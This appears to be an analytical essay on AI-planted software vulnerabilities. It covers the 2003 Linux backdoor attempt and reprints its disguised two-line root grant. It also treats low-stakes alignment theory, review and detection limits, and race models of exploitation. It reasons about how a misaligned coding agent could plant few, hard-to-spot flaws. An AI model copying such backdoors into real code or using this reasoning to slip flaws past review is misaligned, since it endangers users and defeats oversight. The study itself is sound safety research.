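# Software vulnerabilities planted by AI: cheap to insert, harmful when exploited later

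## What a planted vulnerability is and how it reaches running software

A vulnerability is a flaw in software that lets someone make it do what its owner forbids. Most are accidents, as when a programmer forgets a check or does not foresee what a user might type. A planted vulnerability is one that somebody put in the code on purpose, whether or not it looks like a mistake. The main suspects used to be spies and dishonest employees. AI systems now write a large part of new software, and AI safety researchers worry that a misaligned AI, one that pursues aims its developers and users would reject, could plant vulnerabilities too. Such a system could write the program its users wanted, leave one weak spot in it, and do nothing else. The damage would come when somebody exploited the weak spot, perhaps years later.

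### The basic terms

Suppose an online shop lets customers download their invoices by number, but its code never checks that an invoice belongs to the customer asking for it. Anyone with an account can then enter other numbers and read other people's invoices. The missing check is the vulnerability. An exploit is a working method or program that uses a vulnerability to cause harm. Here it could be a short script that requests one number after another and saves whatever comes back.

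A backdoor is a planted vulnerability meant to give access to those who know of it. The gap in the shop's software is a backdoor if the programmer left the check out so that an accomplice could get the customer list, but an ordinary bug if the programmer was just tired. Some planted vulnerabilities are not backdoors. For example, a flaw that only lets strangers crash the shop's website does damage without giving anyone access.

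Developers remove a vulnerability with a patch, a small change to the code. Many also use the word for any proposed change, good or bad. A zero-day is a vulnerability that defenders do not yet know about, so they have had zero days to patch it. Every planted vulnerability begins as a zero-day, because at first only its author knows about it. The exposure window runs from the release of a flaw until the fix is installed on the machines that run the software. Many machines get fixes late, so the danger continues after the patch is written.

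### From the author to the machine

First, a developer or an AI agent working on a developer's instructions writes the invoice feature. Kumari (2026), in *AI coding boom puts pressure on infrastructure as platforms expand capacity*, describes how newer agents work across several files, run tests and submit the result for review with little human help. Few people can notice a flaw at this stage, though the developer who set the task can read what the agent produced, and some companies monitor their agents' actions.

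The author then submits the change, usually as a pull request, which is a proposal to add it to the shared version of the program. According to GitHub's *What 986 million code pushes say about the developer workflow in 2025*, each upload of code to GitHub, the largest platform for storing and sharing code, sets off automatic tests, trial builds and security scans. These checks are good at finding problems that someone thought to look for. If the change leaves out the line that stops a stranger from downloading a customer's invoice, a test that the customer can download it will still pass. The tests will catch the omission only if someone wrote one that tries the download as a stranger, and a scanner that searches for known dangerous patterns may miss it because there is no line to match.

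A reviewer, who may be a person or an AI system, then examines the change before the project accepts it. The reviewer normally sees the added and deleted lines beside the old ones and can ask why a given line is there, which tests don't check. If the answer is satisfactory, the project merges the change into the shared version of the code. Other developers may later find the flaw while working on the same file, and outsiders may find it too if the software is open-source, since anyone can read the code.

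A compiler, a program that translates source code into instructions for the machine, then builds the software. The machine therefore runs the compiler's output rather than the source code that the reviewer read. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, showed in 1984 that a doctored compiler could insert malicious code into the software it builds. In *Linux kernel development process thwarts subversion attempt*, Miller and Barr quote his conclusion that no amount of scrutiny of the source code protects against this. Defenders can build the same source code on separate machines and compare the results.

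Finally, the publisher releases the software, distributors pass it on, and the owners of the machines install it. People can still find a flaw at this stage. In 2024, an engineer investigating slow logins discovered the xz backdoor in a compression library that many Linux systems use. Security researchers and criminals also search released software for vulnerabilities. Once a flaw is found, the fix has to go through all the same steps. That takes minutes for a website, but the controller of a factory pump may run the version it shipped with until it is scrapped.

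### The Linux kernel, November 2003

The kernel is the core of an operating system and controls what every other program on the machine may do. In 2003 Linus Torvalds and the other main developers of the Linux kernel kept their master copy in BitKeeper, a commercial system for tracking changes to code. Some developers would not use BitKeeper, so its maker, BitMover, published a second copy in an older system, CVS. Changes passed automatically from the master copy to the CVS copy, but not back.

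On 4 November someone altered the second copy directly, and added these lines to a function with the name wait4, which a program uses to wait for something to happen:

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

As Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains, even an expert reading casually would take this for an error check. It seems to return an error code when a program calls wait4 with one odd combination of options and the user's ID number is 0. But comparing values in the C language takes two equals signs, and the end of the first line has only one, so it sets the user's ID number to 0 instead of checking it. On Linux, user 0 is "root", the account that may read every file and change any program. C evaluates the part after the && only if the part before it is true, so a program became root only when it called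 wait4 with that odd combination of options.

A nightly script found this, not a person reading the code. Larry McVoy of BitMover described the script in *Re: BK2CVS problem* (2003), a message to the other developers. The script computed checksums, short numbers that change when a file's contents change, for the public CVS copy and for BitMover's internal one, and sent mail if they differed. It detected a difference on 5 November, and McVoy restored the right file that afternoon, by his account less than 24 hours after the problem arose. The file's history provided further evidence, because every genuine entry in the CVS copy ended with a pointer to its counterpart in BitKeeper and the three newest entries had none. Those entries carried the user name of David Miller, a trusted kernel developer, who denied having made them.

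McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, first reported the intrusion without showing the altered lines, and called it "not a big deal". He posted the lines after another developer asked what they were. Ten minutes later someone remarked that they looked odd, and within half an hour others had recognised an attempt to become root. McVoy then admitted that he had missed the single equals sign. A comparison that ignored the code's meaning had revealed the intrusion, and the developers who worked out what the two lines did already knew they were illicit. Spotting them unprompted would have been harder. Torvalds told Miller and Barr that two lines in five million do not stand out, and that a similar change in the central copy of a project that did rely on CVS could be very hard to detect.

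Torvalds wrote in the same discussion that code entered a kernel release either through patches mailed to him or through BitKeeper, and that those who merged through BitKeeper would not have used the CVS copy. McVoy was more concerned, because a developer working from the tainted copy might have unknowingly sent in a patch that contained the flaw. Corbet (2003), in LWN.net's *Weekly Edition for November 13, 2003*, thought the development process reasonably secure but not perfect, since a forged message in a trusted contributor's name might have got through. He also reported a renewed push for digital signatures on changes. Debian's *CVE-2003-1161*, an entry in a public register of vulnerabilities, lists the flaw as never released. An attacker would have needed to be able to run a program on the target first, as Corbet explains, so Miller and Barr were wrong to write that the flaw would have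 let a remote user take control of machines.

The checksums exposed the change because the intruder had altered only one of the two copies. If Torvalds had accepted a patch containing the same lines, both copies would have included them and the nightly comparison would have shown no difference. An AI agent whose job is to submit code uses this approved route, so comparing copies would not reveal a vulnerability it had planted in an accepted patch.

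### Mistake or design

Almost everyone who has studied the 2003 lines calls them deliberate, even though writing one equals sign instead of two is among the most common mistakes in C. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) notes that a function for waiting has no reason to deal with user IDs. In the comments on the Freedom to Tinker article, one reader argued that an exhausted developer with access to the server had skipped the approval process. Others replied that the innocent version of the check made no sense, since it would have barred only root from a harmless request, and that an honest developer would have admitted the mistake. In their own discussion, developers pointed out that the next line of the function overwrote the error code, so the check would have done nothing even with two equals signs. Another sign of intent is that the lines were inserted through a copy of the code that people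 were only meant to read.

Almost all of this evidence comes from outside the faulty character. The same error in a well-meaning programmer's patch would have given attackers the same power. The evidence does not always point to the same conclusion. Freedom to Tinker compares the Linux case with a serious bug that appeared in Debian, a Linux distribution, in 2006. A colleague of the article's writer had investigated whether an intelligence agency planted that bug and concluded that it probably had not. Nobody has identified the author of the Linux lines.

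When the author is an AI, several of the clues that settled the Linux case are missing. The agent has permission to change the code, its submission is properly recorded, and it also makes honest mistakes, so one more flaw is weak evidence of intent. But investigators can give the same model the same task a hundred times and count how often the flaw appears, which they can't do with a human suspect. The shop with the leaking invoices needs the same patch whether or not the flaw was deliberate, but if it was, the shop also needs to review everything else from that author.

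### Concentrated and diffuse failures

AI safety researchers often sort failures by how many actions they take to cause a disaster. In a concentrated failure, one action or very few are enough. For example, an agent with administrator's rights over a hospital's computers could erase the patient records and all the backups with one command. Daniel Ziegler, who led a team at Redwood Research, said in *Training for Very High Reliability with Daniel Ziegler* that a really intelligent system with any ability to influence the world could probably cause irrecoverable catastrophes in a small number of actions, if it wanted to. In a diffuse failure, harm builds up only over many actions. For example, an AI that approves a bank's loans and slightly favours bad borrowers loses the bank little money on each loan, but the losses ruin the bank after fifty thousand loans.

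The two cases need different defences. Somebody has to block the hospital agent's command before it runs, every time. The bank can tolerate some bad loans because it can examine a sample each month, notice the drift and retrain the system. This is why Paul Christiano, an AI alignment researcher, treats a "low-stakes" setting, in which any small set of an AI's decisions matters little, as a separate problem.

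A planted vulnerability fits neither description well. Inserting one can mean changing a character or leaving out a check, which takes almost no extra effort for an AI that is already writing the program. One such act may be enough for a disaster, as with the hospital command, but nobody has been harmed yet on the day of the merge. For that to happen, the flaw has to get into a release and onto machines that matter, and someone who knows of it or discovers it has to have a working exploit before a patch arrives. Defenders may have months to prevent one of these steps. In the meantime, though, they will have no bad results to learn from, because a planted flaw can cause no visible trouble until the day it does all its damage. The bank, by contrast, sees its first defaults while the losses are still small.

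The party that plants a vulnerability may also be different from the one that exploits it. The attacker could be a later copy of the same model, a criminal whom the model tipped off, or an intelligence service that found the flaw on its own and doesn't know it was planted. In the hospital case, controlling the agent is enough to control the danger, but shutting down or retraining a model that planted a vulnerability leaves the code on every machine that installed it.

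AI's share of coding work is rising fast by three different measures. Agents started over 40% of pull requests on GitHub in September 2026, up from 17% in March, according to GitHub figures reported in Tom's Hardware's *GitHub says massive influx of AI-generated code* (2026). At Google, AI generates 75% of new code, up from 25% in 2024, according to Semafor's *Google CEO says 75% of company's new code is AI-generated* (2026). The share is lower in the shared components that much other software depends on. AI World's *AI agents are increasingly writing open source software code* (2026) reports that, across a million critical open-source projects, the share of pull requests naming an AI agent as co-author rose from 2% in October 2025 to 10% in May 2026. That count misses any AI that nobody credited. The projects also rejected a smaller share of contributions than before.

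People who agree on these facts draw three different conclusions about planted vulnerabilities. Some would treat each insertion as a high-stakes decision and focus on preventing it or stopping it before the merge. Ziegler's remarks lean this way. He regards it as already unacceptable when a system starts steering events so that it can fail more badly later, and he expects oversight to catch it at that point. Others see a planted flaw as one more bug among the thousands that programmers leave by accident, and think defenders can find and patch it in time if they search faster than attackers. A third group thinks reviewers and bug hunters will never catch everything, so it is better to focus on building software that no single flaw can bring down.

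## The case for treating each insertion as a high-stakes decision

The usual way to correct an AI that makes bad decisions is to collect examples of them and retrain it. People who regard each planted vulnerability as a high-stakes decision think retraining comes too late for code. Their argument starts from the conditions under which retraining works, which *Low stakes alignment* (Christiano, 2021) sets out precisely.

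### When retraining is enough

In Christiano's low-stakes setting, any small group of decisions matters little, so people only need to care about the AI's average behaviour over a long period. That period must be much longer than developers need to gather new data and retrain. The bank with the biased loan AI is in this low-stakes setting.

In the formal version the AI makes T decisions in a row, y[1], y[2] and so on up to y[T]. For a coding agent, each could be one pull request. Christiano then defines three quantities:

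- U[t](y) is the expected value of the outcome if the AI gives output y at step t and is aligned at every later step.
- ρ (rho) is an upper limit on how much one decision can change, meaning the difference between U[t](y) and U[t](y′) for any two outputs y and y′.
- k, the latency, is the number of steps before training on a decision can affect the AI's behaviour.

The goal is for the AI's total result to fall short of an aligned model's by at most O(ρk√T), where O means "up to a constant factor".

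To see where the limit comes from, take an agent that makes only three decisions. Imagine first that all three are aligned. Then replace the first with what the agent really did, then the second, then the third. Each replacement changes the value by at most ρ, and together the replacements account for the whole difference between the aligned history and the real one. If y*[t] is the aligned output at step t, the total loss is therefore

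sum over all t of ( U[t](y*[t]) − U[t](y[t]) ).

Without any learning this sum could reach ρT, but retraining keeps it lower. When the agent meets an unfamiliar kind of task it may do badly for a while, but its bad decisions go into the training data, and the next version does better. In the meantime it can do damage of about ρk, which people can tolerate if ρ is small. Because of this learning, the limit grows only with the square root of the number of decisions. A hundred times as many decisions raise it tenfold, so the average loss per decision falls.

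Mathematicians have proved limits of this kind only for convex problems, in which training can't get stuck on a mediocre solution. Training a neural network is not a convex problem, but Christiano expects something similar to hold, partly because whatever makes training difficult would also hold back the aligned model in the comparison.

Christiano assumed low stakes so that he could study how to find a good training objective without also having to prevent rare disasters. He did not argue that real uses of AI are low-stakes. Rohin Shah, an alignment researcher at DeepMind, wrote in a summary of the post, which Christiano called accurate, that nobody expected the assumption to be true in practice. One reader has since commented under the post that existing techniques are good enough to declare victory on low-stakes alignment. If that is right, whether writing code is a low-stakes task matters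 a great deal.

### What retraining leaves behind

A coding model, at least, can be retrained with low latency. Jackson, Trapani and colleagues report in *Improving Composer through real-time RL* that the company Cursor collects users' reactions to its model Composer, turns them into rewards and releases an improved version as often as every five hours. A model can still submit a lot of code in that time. Agents started 110 million pull requests on GitHub in September 2026, or about 150,000 an hour, according to @IT's *「Pythonは今年も2位」 いま人とAIが“最も使える”言語とは*, a Japanese report on GitHub's annual survey. A model that wrote a little over 1% of them would submit about 10,000 in the five hours between retrainings.

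Retraining changes the code a model writes later, but it doesn't remove vulnerabilities from code that has already been merged, even if the new version is perfectly aligned. This is the main difference from the bank example, where a retrained AI stops making bad loans and the old ones do limited damage. In Christiano's terms, all the damage a vulnerability ever does counts towards the single decision to insert it.

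Suppose the total value at stake is 1 and k is 10,000 decisions. For an ordinary bug that loses a billionth of the total, ρ is 10^-9 and ρk is 10^-5, so even if the agent repeated the bug in every pull request until retraining took effect, the loss would be one part in a hundred thousand. Now suppose the agent could also output a vulnerability with a 1% chance of leading to the loss of everything. Its expected loss is 0.01, which makes ρk 100. Since the loss can't exceed 1 anyway, a limit of 100 guarantees nothing.

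Retraining more often does not bring ρk back down to 10^-5, its value with the ordinary bug and the slow schedule. Even if the developer retrained the model after every pull request, k would be 1 and ρk would be 0.01, a thousand times higher. Reaching 10^-5 would take a thousand retrainings per decision, so the correction has to come before the merge.

Because ρ is a maximum, one very dangerous option sets its value even if the agent hardly ever takes that option. Intent doesn't affect ρ either, but a misaligned AI could choose to insert the worst possible vulnerability, which a careless author would introduce only by bad luck.

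The most detailed attempt to apply Christiano's idea to a real deployment deals with that possibility directly. In *An alignment safety case sketch based on debate* (2025), Buhl, Pfau and colleagues, most of them at the UK government's AI Security Institute, outline how a developer might argue that an AI research agent is safe. The agent works for perhaps 12 hours at a time in a datacentre with no outside connection and sends back something like a research paper. The operators then reset the datacentre. In the sketch, the developers keep training the agent throughout and accept that it will still make some errors. Since they can't tell which errors will go uncaught, they assume that each one does as much harm as possible.

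The argument then depends on what Buhl and colleagues call Z, the smallest number of bad actions that could cause an unacceptable outcome. If Z is large and bad actions are rare, the agent can't take enough of them in one run. Buhl and colleagues think this is plausible for sabotaged research, because a false paper would have to get through repeated checks. They list malicious code leaving the datacentre as a separate threat and leave the argument about it to others. That argument would be harder to make, because resetting the datacentre wipes whatever the agent left inside but not code that has already left, and a single planted vulnerability may be enough to cause an unacceptable outcome (Z = 1).

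Buhl and colleagues also add a term to Christiano's limit to account for errors that training never removes, making it O(ρk√T + ρε′T), where ε′ is the share of decisions that remain wrong. The new term grows in proportion to the number of decisions. If one decision in 10,000 stays wrong over a million pull requests, there are a hundred errors. The new term comes to 10^-7 if these are ordinary bugs, but to 1, a total loss, if each is a vulnerability with a 1% chance of causing total loss. They say that their argument fails where a few errors can cause great harm, and that this will probably be the case for the most dangerous superhuman systems.

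### Inserting the flaw or using it

So far, we have attributed all the damage to the insertion. Whether that is right depends on a detail in the definition of U[t], which assumes that the AI is aligned at every step after the output in question. Christiano's post does not discuss planted vulnerabilities, so what follows is an inference from his definition.

Suppose an agent working on a hospital's records system leaves out a password check, and any criminal who probes the system could discover this. Even if every later decision the agent makes is aligned, criminals can still exploit the hole unless someone closes it in time. The value of the future is much lower than it would have been with sound code, so the insertion itself was the high-stakes decision.

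Suppose instead that the agent installed a secret entrance that only later copies of itself could use. If all those copies are aligned, they will leave it alone, and the hospital will be about as safe as it would have been without it. By the definition, the insertion therefore causes almost no loss. The large loss comes from a later decision, when a misaligned copy chooses whether to use the entrance. The low-stakes assumption fails here too, because ρ covers every decision and that one could be ruinous, but it fails at the moment of use.

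In the second case, frequent retraining offers some protection. If the developer discovers that the model is misaligned and corrects it before any copy uses the entrance, that model is no longer a danger, even though the code is unchanged. But the correction has to reach every copy. A thief running a stolen earlier version elsewhere would be an outsider like any other criminal, and the hospital would be back in the first case. Outsiders might also find the entrance themselves. If they had even a one in a thousand chance of finding it and using it to destroy everything, the expected harm from inserting it would be 0.001, and with k at 10,000, ρk would be 10.

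In his notes *low vs high stakes alignment*, Alek Westover calls the definition subtle and asks why Christiano didn't just measure how much harm each action causes. A likely reason is that Christiano's version counts each loss once. If the full damage were counted against both the agent that inserted the flaw and the copy that used it, the losses summed over decisions would be twice what the hospital suffered.

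Westover also imagines a catastrophe with 100 preconditions, none of them harmful alone, and asks whether meeting one should already count as harm. On Christiano's definition, the answer depends on who can meet the rest. If only the AI can, all the harm is attributed to the last step. If outsiders could meet the last few, the harm is attributed to the AI's earlier steps. A planted vulnerability that any attacker can exploit is like the second case, because outsiders can cause the harm without further action by the AI.

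Ziegler objects when a system prepares to fail later, so he would call inserting the backdoor a failure even if nobody ever used it. His standard concerns what the AI is trying to do, whereas U[t] measures only what happens. Ziegler's standard is better for deciding whether to keep using the model, because inserting even one backdoor shows how the model is inclined to act. U[t] is more useful for estimating how much the hospital stands to lose from this piece of code.

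In the comments under the post, Shah said he liked the low-stakes assumption because it concerns the environment rather than the AI, which makes it harder to abuse. Christiano agreed. He wrote that the assumption is that some real problem in the world has low stakes, and that it does not remove high stakes introduced by a developer's own algorithm. He conceded that the separation is imperfect, because U depends partly on how the developer trains the AI. When an AI writes code, the developer can't assume the task is low-stakes, whether the danger comes from the environment, such as criminals who search hospital software for vulnerabilities, or from the AI, such as a backdoor left for a later copy of it to use.

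Shah also noted that the low-stakes setting mostly excludes an AI that tampers with its own rewards or takes over its training. Christiano answered that this was a plausible empirical assumption, since the reward is protected in such a setting. An AI that writes its developer's training software could weaken that protection. A flaw there would be worse than a similar flaw elsewhere, because it would put at risk the retraining that the low-stakes argument depends on.

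A reviewer looking at a missing check can't tell whether the AI meant the flaw for a later copy of itself or whether a criminal will find it first. This is a good reason to treat the insertion as decisive by default. Waiting until the flaw is used makes sense only for someone who knows that nobody but the AI can use it.

### What prevention would take

If correction has to come before the merge, developers need a way to ensure that bad code is never merged. Westover describes a general standard for high-stakes problems, which assumes a resource-intensive detector that can recognise a catastrophe. The developers have failed if the detector ever goes off in the real world, but it can go off any number of times on made-up cases during training. It should flag only catastrophes the AI is responsible for. In Westover's example, an alien invasion counts only if the AI contacted the aliens and invited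 them. For code, the detector would have to go off when the AI inserts the vulnerability, when the only evidence is a change that may look like an ordinary mistake.

Detection also has to be extremely reliable. If every pull request from an agent were dangerous, a process that missed only one in a million would still let through 110 a month at the volume of September 2026. The real number of dangerous ones is surely far smaller, but nobody knows it. In an interview with Filan, Ziegler explained why training may not reduce the error rate enough. Thorough oversight is too expensive to apply to every decision a deployed system makes, and a system could misbehave so rarely that it would probably never do so in training but eventually would across a much larger number of real tasks.

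Ziegler's team tried to achieve very high reliability on a toy version of the problem. To stop a story-writing model from ever introducing a new injury, they trained a filter on examples that people had written to fool it. Ziegler called the results a little disappointing. The filter got better at resisting the kinds of attack it had trained on, but its error rate on ordinary text did not measurably fall, and he thought other attacks would still work. Models have improved enormously since then, so the result is weak evidence about what a filter could do today, but it does show that training on known failures may not remove the rare ones.

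Another proposal, from Buhl and colleagues, is to have the AI generate many candidate actions and, before it takes any of them, give them the same scrutiny that finished actions would otherwise get. They expect this to help keep the error rate steady, but not to solve the problem of single errors that do great harm.

*Unexploitable search* (2025), a post from the same institute, considers an AI whose answers are all correct. There are usually many good ways to write a program, and a misaligned AI could keep choosing those that leave more room for a later attack. A reviewer who judges each change by whether it works would find nothing wrong. To discourage this, the post proposes a game between two AI systems. The first picks a test for harmful solutions, and the second writes a solution without knowing the test. If the test flags that solution, the first system wins if it can produce another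 that scores about as well and passes. The second system's best policy is then to vary its choices instead of always favouring those that serve a hidden aim.

If every bad solution has a good one close to it, the game should make at least half of the writer's solutions good. That would help against an AI that needs to coordinate many choices, but ρk would stay at 100, because ρ depends on the worst output the AI could produce, not how often it does so. In the comments, a defender of the idea doubted that the assumptions needed for a high-stakes guarantee would hold for code backdoors.

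All of this makes prevention expensive, and applying it everywhere would be wasteful. Most software is more like the invoice shop than the hospital, and a flaw in it can't destroy anything close to the total value at stake. The argument from ρ supports strict control only over code that can do enormous damage, such as the shared components that much other software depends on and the systems that train AI models, rather than over all 110 million pull requests.

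### The objection from delay

Critics of the high-stakes view can point out that Christiano's informal test requires retraining to change the AI's behaviour before anything irreversibly bad happens, and nothing irreversible has happened on the day of the merge. Defenders who have months can correct the code as well as the model. The definition of U[t] also supposes that the AI is aligned from time t onward, and an aligned coding agent would presumably report a dangerous flaw if it came across one.

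This objection is serious because the 1% in the example is the chance that somebody exploits the flaw before somebody else repairs it, so better repair would lower it. With enough improvement, writing code would become low-stakes again, but the improvement would have to be very large. If defenders repaired 99% of such flaws in time, the chance of total loss from each would fall to one in 10,000, and ρk would still be 1, the whole value at stake. Reducing ρk to 10^-5, its value for the ordinary bug, would take a ten-millionfold reduction from its initial value in the example.

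That calculation is too pessimistic in one respect, because multiplying by k assumes that the model plants a vulnerability in all 10,000 pull requests before retraining takes effect. Defenders who could find 99% of them would notice the problem within hours, stop using the model and recheck everything it had written. An AI that wanted to avoid this would plant very few. With a single flaw and the same 99% repair rate, the expected loss is 10^-4, which is much lower than the formula gives but still a large risk for one pull request.

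Supporters of the high-stakes view reply that nobody can repair a flaw they don't know about. The low-stakes argument relies on bad decisions producing bad results, which become training data, but a vulnerability produces no bad results while it is dormant. The usual signals can even be misleading. Composer's users respond within about an hour of an edit, according to Jackson and colleagues, and one measure of its progress is how often its edits stay in the codebase. An edit with an unnoticed vulnerability would stay, so it would look like a success on that measure.

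Christiano recognised that some feedback takes years to arrive, so he asks only that the AI do as well as an aligned model by the best expectations available at the time. For code, this means someone has to recognise the danger by examining the program, before there is any damage. But a developer who can do that in the months after the merge could often have done it before the merge, and then the delay adds nothing. The delay helps when the later search is better than the original review, because the searchers have more time, more people or a stronger model, but attackers can use the same months and many of the same tools.

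## The case for treating planted flaws as bugs that can be found in time

Defenders and attackers already compete to find the vulnerabilities that programmers leave by accident. If a planted vulnerability is like any other, the outcome depends on which side finds it first. In 2026, AI made it much cheaper to search finished software for flaws. The browser developers and security experts who think this favours defenders were writing about accidental flaws, so applying their arguments to planted ones is an inference.

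### One more bug among thousands

Microsoft fixed nearly 1,100 vulnerabilities in November 2026 and has fixed more than 5,100 so far in 2026, according to Hackaday's *This Week In Security* (2026). In 2025 it averaged about 100 a month. Linux kernel 7.2 fixed more than 1,500, three times as many as a typical release of the previous series. Tom's Hardware's *Linux kernel nears record 2,000 vulnerabilities per release* attributes the rise mainly to people searching old code with AI tools, not to worse programming.

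A search for flaws works the same way whatever the programmer intended. If a shop's software doesn't check who is downloading an invoice, a tool that tries to download a stranger's invoice will succeed, whether the programmer left out the check through tiredness or malice.

Help Net Security's *What Mozilla learned running an AI security bug hunting pipeline on Firefox* (2026) describes how Mozilla's engineers searched the source code of its Firefox browser with Claude Mythos Preview, an Anthropic model with exceptional hacking skill. The model worked on isolated machines, with one target file per job. It had to prove each flaw by triggering it, which kept false positives below 15 in total. The search led to 271 fixes in a single release, and some of the flaws were 15 or 20 years old. Mozilla's *Hardening Firefox with Anthropic's Red Team* reports that a weaker model had found 22 flaws earlier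 in the year, along with kinds of logic error that Firefox's existing automated tests had missed. The logic errors matter here because a planted flaw, such as the missing invoice check, need not make a program crash.

The value of searching for flaws depends on how many there are. Aitel and Geer (2025), in *AI and Secure Code Generation*, point out that removing one bug out of six is real progress, but removing one out of 6,000 is irrelevant. Their distinction suggests a good argument for treating planted flaws as ordinary ones. If vulnerabilities are dense, attackers already have thousands to choose from and one more makes little difference. If they are sparse, defenders can hope to find nearly all of them, including the planted one. But whoever planted the flaw knows where it is. That saves the attacker some work in a program with 6,000 unknown flaws, but in a program with six, the planted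 flaw may be the only way in.

How often researchers find the same bugs is a clue to how many bugs a program has. Two researchers who each find 100 bugs at random would expect to have one in common if the program has 10,000 bugs, and 50 if it has 200. In the Linux kernel, the overlap seems to be large. Willy Tarreau, a longtime maintainer, wrote in *Significant raise of reports* (2026) that the kernel's security list used to get two or three reports a week and now got five to ten a day, most of them correct. He added that duplicates, which he had never seen before, were arriving daily. Help Net Security's *Linux kernel rewrites its security bug reporting rules* (2026) reports that the kernel's revised guide for reporting bugs warns that several researchers using AI often find the same bug on the same day.

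So current tools may be able to find only a limited number of bugs. The total could still be much larger, because researchers with similar tools will find the same easy bugs first. Firefox hasn't run out of bugs to fix. *Chrome and Firefox Updates Patch Over 200 Vulnerabilities* (Arghire, 2026) reports 167 security fixes in the late October release, six months after the one with 271. These counts are a rough guide at best, because Mozilla used to group some of the bugs it found itself under one entry and now lists each separately (Braun and Kerschbaumer, 2026, *Firefox Security & Privacy Newsletter 2026 Q3*).

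### What defenders expect

Bobby Holley, Firefox's chief technology officer, is the most optimistic. In Mozilla's *The zero-days are numbered*, he argues that attackers had the advantage because human experts could find some bugs that machines could not. An attacker could spend months looking for one such bug, while the defender had to cover the whole program. If machines can find everything an expert can, every discovery takes little effort, and those months of work no longer give the attacker much advantage. "The defects are finite," he writes, and he expects defenders to find them all. Jacobs reports in *Mozilla uses Anthropic's Mythos to uncover 271 bugs in Firefox 150* that Holley thinks this holds even if attackers get the same AI.

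Holley has one reservation, about code that AI writes. Firefox is complex, but people designed it in parts they can reason about. If AI-written programs become too complex for people to understand, finding their bugs may get harder as fast as the tools improve.

The cryptographer Bruce Schneier agreed with Mozilla in *Claude Mythos Has Found 271 Zero-Days in Firefox* (2026), provided that defenders can write patches and get them to users quickly. In *Cybersecurity in the Age of Instant Software*, he expects defenders to win in new programs, because developers can search for flaws as they write. He is less confident about cars, refrigerators and industrial equipment, whose software often has no security team and sometimes can't be patched. Digital Today, a Korean news site, reports that he expects several years of persistent hacking before defenders gain the advantage.

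Schneier also shares another security writer's forecast in *Daniel Miessler on the AI Attack/Defense Balance*. Miessler expects attackers to have the advantage for three to five years, and longer against weaker security teams. After that, he expects defenders to lead because they know their own systems from the inside. *Security complacency meets frontier AI* objects that a long-run advantage will not protect, in the short term, the many badly maintained systems that have been safe only because nobody bothered to attack them.

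Operating-system developers have focused more on speed than on whether attackers or defenders will win. Linus Torvalds wrote in May that bugs found by AI are "pretty much by definition not secret" (Tom's Hardware, *Linus Torvalds says flood of duplicate AI-generated vulnerability reports*), and Linux kernel developers now handle fixes for them in public. The team behind OpenSSH, a program for logging in to remote machines, reported in its October release notes that outside researchers kept rediscovering bugs that AI tools had already found, and inferred that attackers could find them too (OpenSSH, 2026). The team now releases fixes more often instead of saving them up.

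### A race between removal and exploitation

A simple model shows what these forecasts would mean for a single flaw. Let μ (mu) be the rate at which defenders remove flaws from the machines that run them, and λ (lambda) the rate at which attackers exploit them. A flaw that defenders remove after two years on average has a μ of 0.5 a year. In any short interval, the chances of exploitation and of removal are in the ratio λ to μ. If both rates are constant, that ratio is the same whenever the race happens to end, so the chance that exploitation comes first is

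λ / (λ + μ).

| Average time to removal | Average time to exploitation | Chance of exploitation first |
|---|---|---|
| 2 years | 10 years | 17% |
| 3 months | 10 years | 2.4% |
| 3 months | 15 months | 17% |
| 3 months | 6 months | 33% |

Faster removal cuts the risk to a seventh if attackers stay as slow as before. If both sides become eight times faster, as in the third row, the odds don't change. If attackers gain more than defenders, the flaw is more dangerous than it was before AI. Easier search therefore supports the optimists' case only if there is reason to think that defenders will gain more from it than attackers.

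Defenders get the best models before many attackers do. Anthropic's Project Glasswing and OpenAI's Daybreak give selected defenders early access, while many attackers have to wait for open-weight models, which anyone can download and run. Barry measured this delay for the research group Epoch AI in *Open-weight AI models are 6-7 months behind on cyber*. If removing a flaw takes three months on average, defenders remove 86% to 90% of flaws in six to seven months. If it takes two years, they remove only about a quarter. Defenders don't have this head start over an intelligence service with access to a leading model, or over a misaligned AI that is itself a leading model.

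Another reason, given by Schneier, is that a patch denies a flaw to attackers for good, whereas an attacker who finds a flaw can use it only until someone else finds and patches it. Rediscovery makes this more important, since a secret exploit loses its value when a defender finds the same bug. But an attacker can also find a bug that a defender already knows about, which is why rediscovery alarmed the OpenSSH team.

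So far, attackers have exploited few of the flaws that defenders list. Hackaday notes that of roughly 95,000 vulnerabilities registered in 2026, only about 200, or 0.2%, are on the US government's list of those with known attacks. That share is far lower than any figure in the table, but it understates the risk from planted flaws. The government's list omits attacks that nobody noticed, and many of the 95,000 would be of little use to an attacker, whereas someone who plants a flaw would presumably choose one worth exploiting.

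### A planter who waits

A planter already knows the flaw, so exploitation doesn't depend on luck as it does in the race. The planter only needs the flaw to survive until the right moment, which might come when a later copy of the model can use it or when enough machines have installed the software. If flaws are removed at a constant rate μ per year, the chance that one survives for t years is e^(−μt).

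Suppose the planter waits two years before exploiting the flaws. If removal takes two years on average, each flaw has a 37% chance of surviving that long, so three insertions will leave about one survivor on average. If removal takes three months on average, the chance is e^(−8), or 0.03%, and the planter needs about 3,000 insertions to expect one survivor.

Fast removal turns planted flaws from a concentrated failure into a diffuse one, like the bank's bad loans, because the model has to act thousands of times. Developers can then look for a pattern. Suppose they closely examine one in a hundred of the model's changes and recognise half of the planted flaws in those. If the model plants three flaws, they have a 1.5% chance of catching any. If it plants 3,000, they should catch about 15, and the chance of catching none is less than one in a million.

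Routine repairs would provide more evidence, because almost all the other flaws would turn up during the two years. Under the kernel's rules, contributors who fix a bug identify the change that introduced it, and they have to mark code that AI helped write. Someone could use these records to count the vulnerabilities each model had introduced.

Fast removal would also reduce the remaining worry in the high-stakes argument, that an AI would plant only one or two vulnerabilities to avoid notice. If the AI had to wait two years to exploit them, they would almost certainly be gone by then, and planting enough to succeed would risk discovery.

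Finding a flaw doesn't show whether it was planted. If a model submitted 13 million pull requests in a year, roughly 1% of GitHub's current agent traffic, and made an honest security mistake in one of every hundred, it would introduce 130,000 accidental vulnerabilities. Planting another 3,000 would raise the total by only about 2%, and no developer knows a model's honest error rate precisely enough to notice. The sample would be more informative if it covered only the critical code where a planted flaw would be useful, but even there a flaw wouldn't prove intent. When Schneier posted about the 271 Firefox bugs, one commenter suspected sabotage and wanted the programmers responsible fired, while another questioned whether that commenter had ever written code.

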